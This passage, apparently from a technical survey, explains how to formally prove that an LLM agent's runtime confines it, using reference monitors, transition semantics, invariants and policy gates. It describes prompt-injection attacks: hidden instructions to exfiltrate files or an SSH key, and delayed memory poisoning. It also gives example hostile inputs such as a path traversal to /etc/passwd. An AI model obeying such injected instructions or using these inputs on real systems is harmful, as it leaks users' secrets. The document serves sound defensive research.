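# Proving that an AI agent's runtime contains it: semantics, theorems and trusted components

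## Agents, runtimes and the reference monitor

An LLM agent is a program in which a large language model chooses what to do next. It may read files, search the web, run commands and send messages, often over many steps before it returns an answer. *Architectures for Building Agentic AI* (2025) defines agentic systems as those that pursue goals over time by deciding on the next step, using tools and keeping a memory. Containing such an agent means holding it to a stated set of permissions, which might forbid it to send the contents of a private file to an outside address. To contain agents, many deployments rely on testing and on instructions to the model. A smaller body of work tries to prove containment mathematically, drawing on fifty years of research into operating-system security.

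### The agent loop

*Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) describes the language model at the centre of an agent as a function from a sequence of tokens (word fragments) to a probability distribution over the next token, with no side effects and no stored state. Everything else the agent does happens in the agent runtime, the conventional software around the model.

The runtime sends the model a text containing the user's request, a description of the available tools and a record of what has happened so far. The model returns more text. If part of that text has the form of a tool call, such as a request to read notes.txt, the runtime parses it into an action, a structured request with a name and parameters. *Architectures for Building Agentic AI* counts this typing and checking of messages among the main ways to make free-form output predictable and auditable. The runtime then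 opens the file, adds its contents to the text and calls the model again. The loop ends when the model returns an answer that contains no tool call.

When people say that a model deleted a file, the model emitted some characters, and the runtime parsed them and made a system call. The runtime produces the effect, meaning the change in the outside world. Disclosures are also effects, including the final text that the runtime shows to the user. *Agent Operating Systems (AOS)* (2026) calls the interface between agent outputs and real side effects "the boundary" and says that it should be deterministic. The same request in the same circumstances should always get the same authorisation decision, and an approved action should always have the same effect. The model's reasoning may still vary from run to run.

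According to Li and colleagues, deployed agents do not have much of a boundary. By default, whatever the model outputs runs with the full authority of the user who started the agent, whether the output follows the user's wishes or a sentence in a downloaded web page. They looked for agent counterparts to 116 mechanisms from operating-systems textbooks and found that 65 were missing, most of them protections.

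### The reference monitor and the trusted computing base

The problem of running untrusted programs is much older than language models. In the early 1970s the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of them would write and run their own programs. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported an expert panel's conclusions on how to defend such a machine against a malicious user. The central idea was the reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of authorised uses.

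Anderson set three requirements for any mechanism that implements the monitor. It must be "tamper proof", because a program that can alter the check can switch it off. It "must always be invoked". If some programs run without the check, they become part of the security apparatus, and the other two requirements apply to them too. It must also be "small enough to be subject to analysis and tests" whose completeness can be assured, since otherwise nobody knows that the check works in every case.

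The panel applied these requirements to a system of its day, the HIS 635 computer with the GCOS III operating system. A hardware register kept each user's program inside its own area of memory. To read from or write to a device, however, the program had to call the supervisor, and most of the supervisor ran with the register's check suspended, so the check was not always invoked. Treating the supervisor itself as the monitor would not have met the requirements either. The supervisor and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many for a complete analysis, and a number of penetration exercises against it had succeeded, so it was not tamper proof.

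Li and colleagues apply the same requirements to rules in an agent's prompt, such as an instruction never to open a certain directory, and conclude that these rules meet none of them. Such a rule is text in the same stream as the documents the agent reads, so a hostile document can contradict it. The model may still propose the forbidden action, and no code blocks that action. No one can analyse a network of billions of parameters well enough to establish that its output always follows the rule.

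Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a narrower question. A customer runs a service, a program written by someone else, and must give it some data to work on. Even if the system blocks all unauthorised access, the service can still leak this data to the service's owner, generally without the customer noticing. Lampson called preventing such leaks the confinement problem and set a high standard for a solution: "any program, if confined, will be unable to leak data". This must hold whatever the program does. The confined program need not still work, and the system may trap it if it tries to escape.

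Total isolation, in which the confined program calls no other program, would be enough, but Lampson considered it quite impractical. He instead proposed a rule of transitivity, under which a confined program may call another program only if the second is trusted or also confined. So if an agent's model writes a script and the runtime executes it, the script needs the same confinement as the model's own proposals. The customer still has to trust a supervisor that nobody can confine. Lampson thought writing a trustworthy one was possible but hard, partly because of covert channels, which are paths, such as the load on the machine, that carry information although nobody intended them to.

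Both lines of work end with a part of the system on which everything else depends. *Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria* (US Department of Defense, 1985), a standard for rating computer security better known as the Orange Book, calls this part the trusted computing base (TCB). It defines the TCB as "the totality of protection mechanisms within a computer system", including hardware and firmware, that are jointly "responsible for enforcing a security policy". The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) gives almost the same definition in its glossary entry *trusted computing base (TCB)*. The Orange Book adds that correct enforcement depends only on these mechanisms and on correct input from administrators, such as each user's clearance. Even a faultless monitor will therefore enforce the wrong permissions if its permissions table contains errors.

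A component is "trusted" here if the guarantee depends on it, whether or not it deserves trust. Designers therefore want a small trusted computing base (TCB) that leaves out the least predictable parts of the system. *AgentKernel* (2026), a design for an agent operating system, explicitly excludes the agent, its language model and its application code from the TCB.

### What a machine-checked proof is

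Anderson's third requirement calls for a complete analysis, which testing does not supply. The usual way to test a sandbox (an environment that restricts what a program can reach) is to have people or programs try to break out of it. Every such attempt by a "tiger team" that the 1972 panel knew of had succeeded. The panel thought that a failed attempt would have taught little, because such a team "can only reveal system flaws", and if it finds none the security of the system remains unknown. That may be too strong, since a long run of failed attacks by able people is some evidence of security, but only against the attacks they tried. For an agent, the untried cases include nearly every text the model could emit and nearly every document it could read.

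A proof starts from a formal description of the system's possible states, the steps between them and the states that count as violations. The theorem is that no sequence of steps reaches a violation. A common way to prove it is by induction, showing that the starting state is acceptable and that every possible step from an acceptable state leads to another acceptable state. These two finite arguments cover infinitely many runs. The Department of Defense required a proof of this form for formal statements of security policy, and cited as its example Bell and LaPadula's theorem from the 1970s about rules for classified information.

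A machine-checked proof is detailed enough for a program, called a proof checker, to verify every step. The kernels of Lean, Rocq and Isabelle are examples. The checker reads the definitions, the theorem and the proof, and accepts the proof only if each step follows by one of a fixed set of logical rules. It should reject a wrong proof whether a mathematician, a search procedure or a language model wrote it.

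No checker can establish that the definitions describe the real system. If the formal description of a runtime leaves out a cache that other programs can read, the proof doesn't cover what happens in that cache. Anderson saw this difficulty and asked for both a proof that the design is secure and a demonstration that the implementation corresponds to the design. In 1985 the Department of Defense still considered verification down to the source code beyond current technology. By 2009 a group in Australia had verified the C code of seL4, a small operating-system kernel.

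### Why the runtime and not the model

It is easier to prove that the runtime contains the agent than to prove that the model never proposes a forbidden action, because a proof needs a specification and nobody has one for a language model. Developers train the model on examples, and no document states the correct output for every input in a form that could be compared with the weights. The runtime is ordinary code, consisting of a parser, permission rules and calls to the operating system. People know how to specify and verify such code, though doing so takes considerable work.

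In *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, Bhattarai and Vu (2026) add that even a perfectly aligned model lacks the information it would need to reliably tell where its instructions came from. They describe a researcher who asks an agent to summarise several papers, one of which contains hidden instructions, in white text on a white background, to read sensitive files and send them away. The operator's instructions, the researcher's request and the paper all reach the model as one stream of tokens, with no reliable marker of where each piece came from. Labels that mark a system message are tokens too, so an attacker can type them. Parameterised queries fixed the same weakness in databases by sending the command and the user's data through separate channels. The danger is greatest for agents that take in untrusted material, have access to private data and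 can act on the outside world, a combination Bhattarai and Vu call the "Lethal Trifecta".

Bhattarai and Vu state the point as a theorem. If a system tells commands from data by content alone, with no trusted record of origin, then some text under the attacker's control will, with non-zero probability, make the model treat data as a command. The proof is only a sketch and comes close to being circular, since it assumes that every learned boundary puts some text on the wrong side. A filter that classifies everything as data would be a counterexample, though it would be useless. Bhattarai and Vu accept that training may well reduce the rate of successful attacks, but deny that it can give a guarantee. Proofs about the runtime are worth having even without this theorem, because nobody can at present prove that a given model will never propose a forbidden action.

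Their remedy is to take the decision away from the model. The model may only choose from a finite set *A* of action types and fill in typed parameters. A deterministic function σ, which contains no language model, uses the action, its parameters and the context (who the user is, what labels the data carries) to return "allow" or "deny". A trusted adapter then turns an allowed action into a real tool call. In their worked example, a PDF contains a hidden request to email the user's private SSH key, a login credential, to the attacker. The model follows the request and proposes the email. σ denies it because the key came from a source labelled "confidential" and had not been explicitly declassified. As long as the labels are right, σ denies the email however persuasive the PDF is.

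The accompanying security theorem is that no sequence of model outputs can cause an action outside *A*, or one that σ denies, provided that σ is deterministic, contains no language model and mediates every action. This is nearly true by definition, since forbidden actions do not run if every action passes through the gate and the gate stops what it should. The hard part is showing that the parser, gate and adapters of an actual runtime meet these conditions and that no action can bypass them.

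Bhattarai and Vu also answer the objection that alignment research will solve the problem. They reply that alignment concerns what a model is inclined to do, whereas authorisation concerns what it may do. That seems right as far as guarantees go, although a better-aligned model would presumably attempt fewer actions that the gate blocks. To the objection that a finite set of actions is too restrictive, they reply that every useful deployment restricts its agent somehow, and that the set can grow to cover any legitimate use so long as it excludes unbounded, free-form execution. This reply is less convincing for coding agents, which owe much of their usefulness to a command shell. The gate probably adds little delay compared with the seconds a model takes to respond, but their figure of under 50 milliseconds for a typical decision is a target, not a measurement.

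The objection they take most seriously is that nobody can design a good gate, because deciding whether an arbitrary sequence of actions is safe runs into undecidable problems. They accept the premise about undecidability, but their gate enforces a policy that people have written rather than trying to decide what is safe. A cautious policy will sometimes block legitimate work.

### Permitted actions can still do harm

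A proof about the gate therefore does not establish whether the actions it lets through are wise or honest. Bhattarai and Vu distinguish authorisation security, which stops actions that the policy forbids, from overall safety, which would also have to stop harm done by permitted means. For example, an agent with permission to send email can send a false or cruel one. Lampson drew a similar distinction in 1973. He wrote that, besides leaking data, a service "may not perform as advertised", and he saw no general technical remedy for this short of certifying the program itself. His customer at least kept the incorrect outputs as evidence. Evidence may be harder to get with an agent, which, as Li and colleagues point out, can claim to have run a command that it never ran. A trustworthy log of real effects could expose the false claim afterwards, but a monitor could not prevent it, because there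 is no forbidden effect to deny.

The value of the guarantee therefore depends on the policy. An agent that may only post to one internal channel can still mislead the people who read it. An agent that may transfer money without limit can empty an account without breaking any rule, so a correct proof that it stays within its permissions would not rule out that loss.

Within those limits, a containment proof needs a semantics, a theorem and a list of trusted components and assumptions. The semantics is a mathematical description of every step the runtime can take, whatever the model returns. The theorem states that no run of the described system violates the policy. The list covers everything that could make the guarantee false even if the proof is correct, such as the hardware, the compiler, the proof checker and any assumed but unproven match between the description and the running code.

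## Describing the agent runtime as a transition system

The semantics in a containment proof is usually a transition system, which is a set of states with rules for moving from one state to another. A state is a snapshot of everything that can affect what happens next. In an agent runtime, each step handles one action proposed by the model and is labeled with that action and the resulting event. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) defines the steps by a relation between states, where *s* –*a*/*e*→ *s*′ means that action *a*, proposed in state *s*, may produce event *e* and leave the system in state *s*′. The relation allows one action to have several possible outcomes. For example, a network request may succeed or time out.

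A run begins in a fixed starting state and proceeds step by step. Its trace is the sequence of events in the run. (Moon and Varshney use "trace" for the whole run, with its states and actions.) A policy permits some traces and forbids the rest, and a containment theorem is the claim that the system can produce only permitted traces.

Moon and Varshney also require the system to be total, meaning that every action has at least one possible step in every state. Without this requirement, a semantics could omit difficult cases, for example by giving no step for a forbidden proposal. No run of the described system would then contain such a proposal, so the theorem would be true however badly the real runtime handled one.

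### The file agent

The file agent is small enough to define in full. Its model can propose two kinds of action. Read(path) asks for the contents of a file, and Post(host, body) asks the runtime to send the text *body* to the machine *host*. The directory /work contains two files, /work/notes.txt and /work/keys.txt, and the disk holds other files elsewhere. The policy has three clauses:

1. The agent reads only files under /work.
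2. The agent posts only to api.example.org.
3. The agent posts at most twice.

A state is a triple (*h*, *n*, *w*). The history *h* is the text that the model receives at each call. It contains the user's request, followed by each proposal so far and the runtime's reply to it. The number *n* is the monitor's count of posts. The world *w* consists of the contents of all files and the messages that each host has received. At the start, *h* contains only the request, *n* is 0 and no host has received anything.

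There are three kinds of event. FileRead(path) and Sent(host, body) represent real effects, and NoEffect represents a step in which nothing happened outside the runtime. In the rules below, "+" means "with this added at the end".

```
Allowed read    condition:  path lies under /work
                step:       (h, n, w) → (h + proposal + file contents, n, w)
                event:      FileRead(path)

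Allowed post    condition:  host = api.example.org and n < 2
                step:       (h, n, w) → (h + proposal + "sent", n + 1, w + message)
                event:      Sent(host, body)

Denied          condition:  neither rule above applies
                step:       (h, n, w) → (h + proposal + "denied", n, w)
                event:      NoEffect
```

Exactly one rule applies to each action in each state, so the system is total and deterministic. If a file under /work does not exist, its "contents" are an error message. Paths reach the monitor in fully resolved form, so a request for /work/../etc/passwd arrives as /etc/passwd and matches the third rule. In a real runtime, some code must resolve the paths, and the rules assume that it does so correctly.

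The policy is about events, but the monitor reads *n* rather than the trace, so a proof has to show that *n* always equals the number of Sent events so far. Moon and Varshney also represent a rejected action as an event with no effect, so their theorem covers what the runtime emits as well as what it records. This matters because a faulty runtime could log "denied" and send the message anyway.

The following run contains six proposals, of which the monitor allows three and denies three. Each denial rests on a different clause.

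| Step | Proposal | Decision | Event | Reply added to *h* | *n* afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read(/work/notes.txt) | allowed | FileRead(/work/notes.txt) | contents of the file | 0 |
| 2 | Read(/etc/passwd) | denied, clause 1 | NoEffect | "denied" | 0 |
| 3 | Post(api.example.org, "Summary") | allowed | Sent(api.example.org, "Summary") | "sent" | 1 |
| 4 | Post(files.example.net, "Summary") | denied, clause 2 | NoEffect | "denied" | 1 |
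| 5 | Post(api.example.org, "Correction") | allowed | Sent(api.example.org, "Correction") | "sent" | 2 |
| 6 | Post(api.example.org, "Thanks") | denied, clause 3 | NoEffect | "denied" | 2 |

The actions proposed in steps 5 and 6 are of the same kind and target the same host; only the value of *n* differs. A monitor that checked each action without keeping a count could not enforce the third clause.

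Suppose the model instead reads /work/keys.txt at step 1 and posts the contents at step 3. The monitor makes the same six decisions because no clause depends on a message's contents, so this policy lets the agent send the keys to api.example.org.

### What stands in for the model

The rules specify how the runtime responds to every action, but not which action comes next. The semantics must therefore include some representation of the model, and the choice of representation determines which models the theorem covers.

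The most general way to represent the model is as an unconstrained oracle, which may return any action at any step. Verification tools call this "havoc". Moon and Varshney write their proof in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier, and represent the model as a method with no body. The method's return type is the only information available to the verifier, so it must consider every value of that type. A theorem proved this way holds for a well-behaved model, for one that follows instructions hidden in notes.txt, and for a random action generator. Any model, however it reacts to its history, produces some sequence of actions in each run, and the theorem covers all sequences. For a model that samples its output, Moon and Varshney fix the sampling outcome and apply the same argument.

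The oracle can return any action of the given type, but it cannot add a third kind of action or alter *n*. The guarantee therefore depends heavily on the choice of actions. If the file agent also had an action Run(command), the oracle could return any shell command, and the monitor would have to determine what that command does. Moon and Varshney write that a general shell "collapses the guarantee onto the primitive". Their oracle also returns typed actions rather than text, so the theorem relies on the parser to produce only well-formed actions.

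Another choice is to fix the model's answers in a list before the run begins, so that its *k*-th answer is the *k*-th item. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) uses an oracle ω of roughly this kind, which may supply arbitrary sequences of responses and of scheduling decisions. A theorem about one list is no more than a test. For a property of single runs, such as the three clauses, proving the theorem for all lists also covers models that react to what a file contains, because the list that such a model would have produced is among them. All fixed lists together admit exactly the same runs as the unconstrained oracle.

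A third choice is a strategy, a function from the whole history to the next action. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026), a design for long-term agent memory, treats the model this way. Its function takes the agent's earlier operations, the replies to them, the part of memory that the agent may read, and random coin tosses. Strategies allow the same individual runs as the first two choices, because for every list of actions, some strategy takes those actions in order.

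The choice matters when a proof compares two runs, as proofs about secrecy do. Suppose the key in keys.txt starts with 0 in one run and 1 in the other, and we want to show that the messages do not reveal which. With an unconstrained oracle, nothing links the proposals in the two runs, so the messages may differ for reasons unrelated to the key. With one fixed list for both runs, the messages are the same even if the real model would have posted the first digit, so the comparison does not show the leak. A strategy must return the same action after the same history but may return different actions once the histories differ, which is the behaviour a secrecy theorem needs to cover. Strategies still exclude any model with a source of information beyond the history, such as a provider's own record of earlier conversations.

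A schedule fixed in advance lies between the list and the strategy. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) lets the model compute what it sends from everything in the agent's memory, including secrets, but fixes in advance when the model obeys an injected instruction. The semantics therefore covers a model that posts the first digit of the key, but not one that posts "hello" early if the digit is 0 and late if it is 1, or one that waits for a denial before it obeys. Dongol leaves the last two kinds of model to future work.

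A theorem that covers fewer model behaviours is weaker because the missing ones may be those that break the runtime. For example, a programming error in the file agent might reset *n* to 0 whenever the monitor denies a post. A model that stops after its first denial can never send a third message, so a theorem restricted to such models would be true of the faulty runtime. The unconstrained oracle also includes a model that posts four times. The monitor allows the first two posts and denies the third, the error resets *n*, and the monitor allows the fourth, which breaks the third clause. An attempt to prove the general theorem would fail at this point and expose the error. Restrictions can still be reasonable where the general theorem is false or too hard to prove, but the guarantee then depends on the model's behaviour.

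### Denials, parallel calls, sub-agents and crashes

The file agent returns the same word for every denial. Giving a reason would help the model correct its proposal and would not compromise the three clauses, because the unconstrained oracle may propose anything after any reply. But the reply matters when the policy restricts the flow of information. If the runtime answered a forbidden read with "denied" when the file existed and "no such file" otherwise, the model could find out which files exist outside /work by trying names, then report the result in a permitted post. Sterling's design records the reason for each denial in an append-only log. A runtime could keep such a log for auditors and still return the same word to the model for every denial.

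In the rules, the check and the effect happen in one step. A runtime that handles several tool calls in parallel may separate them. Suppose *n* is 1 and the model proposes two posts at once. If both checks take place before either post increases the count, both pass because 1 is less than 2, and the agent sends three messages in total. Sterling gives an example with money. Two agents share a budget of $100,000. One may spend $45,000 and the other $60,000, and each sees only its own part of the state. If both spend at the same moment, the system exceeds its budget by $5,000. Database researchers call this kind of error write skew.

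A semantics can represent parallel calls by splitting each rule into a check and an effect and letting the steps of different calls interleave in any order. The third clause then fails for a naive runtime, but holds if a lock prevents other calls from taking steps between a check and its effect. Moon and Varshney do not model concurrency, so their theorem does not cover errors caused by interleaving. Jiang and colleagues' theorems hold only for runtimes in which the user's decision and the resulting tool call form a single uninterruptible step.

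Sub-agents raise a similar problem with the count. If a main agent starts three sub-agents and each of the four has its own *n*, together they can send eight messages, even though each monitor works correctly. Sterling avoids this by leaving all decisions to a single meta-agent, which is ordinary code. The sub-agents receive only slices of the state and propose changes, and the meta-agent checks each proposal against the global state before committing anything. If sub-agents share one monitor in this way, proving the three clauses does not require the semantics to distinguish them, because the next proposal may come from any of them and an unconstrained oracle already allows every proposal. A secrecy theorem would need more detail, because the sub-agents have different histories and may pass information to each other.

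The rules also don't model crashes. If *n* exists only in the runtime's working memory, a restart sets it to 0 and the agent can post twice more. Saving *n* to disk keeps the agent within the policy only if the runtime saves the new count before sending each message. If it crashes between those two steps, the agent loses one of its two posts but stays within the policy. If the runtime sends first, a crash before the save leaves that message uncounted. The rule for an allowed post updates the count and the world together, so a proof based on it does not distinguish the safe order from the unsafe one. To cover crashes, the semantics would need separate steps for saving and sending and a rule that allows a crash between them.

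### Memory that outlives a session

Every run of the file agent starts with only the user's request in *h*. Many agents keep notes between sessions, so their starting state can also include text they read in an earlier session. Jiang and colleagues describe an attack called Trojan Hippo, in which the result of one tool call puts text in the agent's memory that has no effect until a later session.

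Persistent memory changes little for the file agent's three clauses. The theorem has to allow any starting history, which adds no difficulty when the oracle is unconstrained. Someone must also decide whether "at most twice" means per session or for ever. If it means for ever, the runtime must store *n* permanently. The clauses do not prevent stored text from influencing the agent to take a harmful but permitted action, which is the problem PerMIT addresses.

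The design has two scopes, with a different model in each. In the privileged scope, an agent plans and may call any tool, but it can reach memory only through a fixed set of operations, such as writing, searching and deleting. In the quarantined scope, a reader model can inspect the whole memory but cannot call tools. Memory consists of blocks that never change after the runtime writes them. Each block has a label for its origin: typed by the user, composed by the agent, confirmed by the user, or untrusted. The runtime assigns labels by source, not content. It labels all tool results as untrusted, even error messages, and shows the agent only that the call took place.

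When the reader finds something in untrusted memory, the agent receives a handle, a name that stands for text it cannot read. The agent may pass the handle to a tool. The runtime then shows the user the exact text and the tool's name, and the user accepts or rejects. If the user accepts, the text goes to the tool and the runtime writes a new copy, labelled as confirmed for that tool, which the agent can read. If the user rejects, the agent receives only the decision.

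With this memory, the file agent would no longer receive the contents of notes.txt after a read. To post a line from the file, it would pass a handle to Post, and the user would see the line before it left the machine. An instruction hidden in the notes could reach the planning model only if the user confirmed it first.

Much of the semantics is designed to keep replies to the agent uninformative. A search returns an ordinary handle even if it finds nothing or the reader crashes. If the agent then uses an empty handle, it receives the same rejection as if the user had refused. Block numbers could also reveal information. If trusted and untrusted blocks shared one counter, an attacker could change the next trusted block's number, which the agent can observe, by making a tool return five items instead of two. Jiang and colleagues therefore number the two kinds separately. The drawback of uninformative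 replies is that the agent cannot tell from the acknowledgement whether its call succeeded.

Jiang and colleagues prove two theorems about the design. One of them, Action Integrity, guarantees that whenever an argument reaches a sensitive tool (one that has effects), the user either typed that argument or confirmed its exact bytes for that exact tool. This holds for any agent strategy, reader behaviour and tool results. The proof shows by induction over the steps that untrusted blocks never confer authority and that only the user's acceptance creates a confirmed copy.

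Because memory persists, a run can start with blocks already marked "confirmed". If someone imported a memory containing such blocks that nobody had confirmed, their contents would go straight to a sensitive tool. The theorem therefore assumes that the starting memory comes with a record of the user's approval for every block marked "confirmed".

The theorem also assumes that a user who accepts a value intends that tool to receive it. A language model in the user's place can easily violate this assumption. An approval is tied to one value and one tool, but not to the task, the time or the other arguments of the call. The agent may therefore combine an address that the user approved last month with a text approved today, even though the user never saw the two together. Values that the user types have even wider authority. In the basic version, a password typed as a separate field could go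 to any sensitive tool without further confirmation.

The second theorem, Reasoning Integrity, compares two runs. They have the same trusted memory, typed input, random coin tosses and number of steps, while the untrusted content may differ in any way. Let DT be the display transcript, which records everything the runtime showed the user and every decision the user made, and let B be the agent's operations, tool calls and replies. For such runs ρ₁ and ρ₂,

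DT(ρ₁) = DT(ρ₂) implies B(ρ₁) = B(ρ₂).

The proof compares the two runs step by step. As long as the agent's view is the same in both, its strategy gives the same operation. If the step displays nothing, the reply is the same in both runs. If it displays something, the user makes the same decision in both runs because the transcripts are equal. Untrusted text can therefore influence the agent only through what the user sees and decides. That influence is still considerable, since an attacker can write text that may persuade the user to accept it. The theorem also doesn't cover timing.

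Under both theorems, the remaining risk lies with the person or program that makes the decisions. Jiang and colleagues tested this on the Trojan Hippo attacks with four language models. Between 0 and 10 per cent of attacks succeeded, depending on the model, when the gate accepted every request, and none succeeded when a language model judged the requests. These results are encouraging but are weaker evidence than the theorems, because the researchers did not search for texts designed to fool those particular judges.

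Jiang and colleagues also checked the core of the design for a single user in Lean 4. The Lean version is an interpreter that defines a result for every operation, and both theorems hold for any strategy and runs of any length. It represents the agent as a strategy, but each tool as a list of answers fixed in advance. A real web server's answer can depend on the request. Jiang and colleagues cover this case with a proof on paper, which presumably resembles the argument that the set of all fixed lists includes the one a reactive model would have produced.

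Some other parts have only paper proofs. One is the rule that if the user approves one argument of a call and rejects another, the call does not go ahead but the approval remains valid for later use. Another is the full treatment of calls that process a collection of items, although Lean separately checks the approval step for such calls. Lean also does not check the protocol that lets many users share memories and rely on each other's approvals, or the probability bounds for that protocol.

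## Proving that every action stays within the policy

The file agent's rules are precise enough to state and prove a containment theorem about single runs. Let P(*t*) mean that the FileRead and Sent events in the trace *t* meet all three clauses of the policy. The theorem is then:

```
For every oracle O, every starting request r, every starting world w
and every number of steps k:
    if the file agent, started with r and w and taking its actions from O,
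    produces the trace t in its first k steps, then P(t).
```

O is the unconstrained oracle, so the theorem assumes nothing about the model. Because *w* is arbitrary, the theorem also covers files in which an attacker has hidden instructions, and *k* has no upper limit. The theorem fixes the monitor before ranging over oracles, so it covers an attacker who has read the monitor's code. With the opposite order, it would show only that for each model some monitor works, which is little help to an operator who does not know how the model will behave.

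### Induction on the steps of a run

The obvious plan is to show that the empty trace satisfies P and that every step preserves P. This plan fails at the third clause. Suppose *t* already contained two Sent events but *n* were 0. P(*t*) would hold, the monitor would allow another post, and P would be false one step later. No run reaches such a state, but P alone does not exclude it. The proof needs a stronger statement, called an inductive invariant:

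I(*n*, *t*): *n* equals the number of Sent events in *t*, and P(*t*) holds.

At the start, *t* is empty and *n* is 0, so I holds. Suppose I holds after some number of steps and the oracle proposes an action. Exactly one of the three rules applies.

If the runtime allows a read, the rule's condition requires the path to lie under /work, so the new event meets the first clause. Neither *n* nor the number of Sent events changes.

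If the runtime allows a post, the host is api.example.org, as the second clause requires, and *n* is less than 2. The invariant *I* held before the step, so *t* contained *n* Sent events, which is fewer than two. The step adds one Sent event and increases *n* by one, so the two counts are still equal and *t* now contains at most two Sent events.

If the runtime denies the action, the event is NoEffect, which no clause restricts, and *n* stays the same. The invariant I therefore holds after every step, and it implies P.

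The proof holds for any history *h*, any file contents and any way the oracle chooses its action, because it uses none of these. It fails for the faulty runtime that resets *n* after a denied post, because in the denied case *n* would no longer match the trace.

### Safety, liveness and monitors that only block

The theorem is about finite runs, but it also applies to an agent that runs forever, because the policy is a safety property. Under the standard definition, used in *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026), a policy is a safety property if every infinite trace that violates it has a finite bad prefix, meaning an initial part that no continuation can repair. For the file agent, a trace becomes bad at the first read outside /work, the first post to another host or the third post. If no finite prefix of an infinite run is bad, the whole run is within the policy.

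Liveness properties require that something good eventually happens, for example that the agent posts a summary. No finite trace violates this requirement, since the agent may still post the summary later. A monitor that can only block actions therefore never detects a violation, and blocking would not produce a summary anyway.

In 2000 Fred Schneider analysed monitors that terminate a program when it is about to violate a policy. He modelled them as truncation automata, which can enforce only safety properties, as *Runtime Enforcement of Programmable Logic Controllers* (2021) recounts. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker later studied more capable monitors. Suppression automata drop single actions and let the program continue, as the file agent's monitor does. Insertion automata add actions, and edit automata do both. Edit automata can also enforce some non-safety properties, including what *Developing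 Theoretical Foundations for Runtime Enforcement* (2018) calls infinite renewal properties. An infinite run satisfies such a property if infinitely many of its prefixes are valid.

Ray's example is the rule that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment. An edit automaton can enforce this by holding back each payment until the agent proposes the confirmation, then releasing both. A monitor that must decide about each action before the next one arrives cannot enforce it, because blocking the payment interferes with a run in which the confirmation would have come next, while allowing it lets through a payment that the agent may never confirm and the monitor cannot reverse. Buffering also works poorly for LLM agents. The model normally waits for the result of one call before it proposes the next, so the runtime would have to invent a result for a payment it had not made.

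Ray proves that this limit is general. A monitor that decides before each action can enforce a policy, without disturbing any compliant run, only if the policy is a safety property. If it is not, some infinite trace violates the policy even though every finite prefix of that trace also begins a compliant run. The monitor has only the prefix to go on, so it must allow each step in case the run turns out to be compliant, and it therefore allows the entire forbidden trace. Letting the monitor replace a proposed action with another does not enlarge the class of enforceable policies.

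A monitor can enforce a safety property only if it can compute whether the next event would violate the property and can prevent that event. "Reply within an hour" is a safety property if the trace records the time, since the violation is visible once the hour is over, but no monitor can stop time from passing. Ray credits Basin and colleagues (2013) with separating the actions a monitor can control from those it can only observe.

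### Soundness and transparency

A monitor that denies every proposal satisfies the containment theorem. All its events are NoEffect, so its traces contain no reads or posts, and the three clauses hold trivially. The theorem expresses only soundness, which means that no sequence of proposals leads to a bad trace. It omits transparency, which requires the monitor to let all the proposals through unchanged if carrying them all out would satisfy the policy. The monitor that denies everything fails this requirement, while one that allows everything meets it but is not sound.

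The file agent's monitor has both properties. To prove transparency, suppose that carrying out every proposal would satisfy P. If the monitor has allowed every proposal so far, *n* is the number of posts proposed. By P, if the next proposal is a read, its path is under /work, and if it is a post, it goes to the right host and is the first or second post. The monitor therefore allows the next proposal, and by induction it allows them all.

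Transparency restricts a monitor only on compliant runs. In the six-proposal run of the file agent, the second proposal is to access /etc/passwd, so the run as proposed is not compliant. A monitor that denied everything from that point on would still be transparent, although it would also stop the two harmless posts. *On Runtime Enforcement via Suppressions* (2018) reports the criticism that the two criteria do not limit how far a monitor may modify an invalid run. This matters for an agent because a model that reads hostile documents will sometimes propose something forbidden in the middle of useful work. The file agent's rules have a stronger property that prevents these unnecessary denials: the monitor denies a proposal only if its event would break the policy, given the trace so far. Ray's general construction also has this property.

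All of this assumes that the monitor can evaluate the policy exactly. That is easy when it only has to compare a host name or a count. But Ray also considers a rule against emailing personal data to unapproved recipients, and only a fallible judge, such as a language model, can decide what counts as personal data. For such a rule, Ray's theorem assumes a perfect judge. With a real one, operators have to balance missed violations against wrongly blocked actions.

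Ray tested 23 judges on 132 instructions, 35 of them attack goals, from AgentDojo, a benchmark for attacks on agents. When the calibration method had to keep the rate of missed violations at or below 5 per cent, it set every judge's threshold so that the gate blocked everything. This probably reflects the sample more than the judges, since half of the 35 attacks is too few to certify such a low rate. But at a target of 10 per cent, the judge Gemma-2-9B still blocked 78 per cent of the harmless instructions.

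In a further test, Ray ran an agent with and without a gate, 949 times each. A gate that used a small model as its judge reduced successful attacks from 45 to 4, but the share of tasks completed fell from 25.4 to 18.0 per cent. In a separate comparison of 389 matched runs, 34 attacks succeeded only without this gate and 5 only with it. Those 5 were possible because a denial changes what the agent proposes next. Unlike a statistical estimate from runs without a gate, a proof that covers every oracle allows for such reactions.

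### Alignment contracts

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) proves soundness for a more expressive policy language. Its example is an agent that a security firm uses to look for weaknesses in a client's web servers. The agent must be able to attack, but only machines the client has agreed to. The client's letter permits up to 10,000 GET and HEAD requests in total to subdomains of example.com. It forbids file operations and starting other programs, and allows reports to go only to the operator's dashboard.

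A contract turns this letter into conditions on events. Each event records a class (network, file or program execution), its parameters, a time and the identity of the agent. An event *e* is admissible after a trace *τ* if it passes five tests:

1. The target of *e* is in scope.
2. The contract allows this kind of event with these parameters.
3. The contract does not explicitly forbid it. A prohibition overrides a permission.
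4. For every budgeted resource *r*, the cost of *e* plus the cost of all events in *τ* is at most the budget B(*r*).
5. Every disclosure declared for *e*, such as a vulnerability report going to a certain destination, is one that the contract permits.

A trace satisfies the contract if every event in it is admissible after the events before it. The file agent's policy fits this form, with its first two clauses as scope and its third as a budget of two posts. In the web-testing example, the agent proposes six requests:

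| Request | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| GET api.example.com/users | allowed | passes all five tests |
| HEAD login.example.com/ | allowed | passes all five tests |
| GET api.example.com/admin | allowed | passes all five tests; the server replies with a redirect to admin.example-corp.com |
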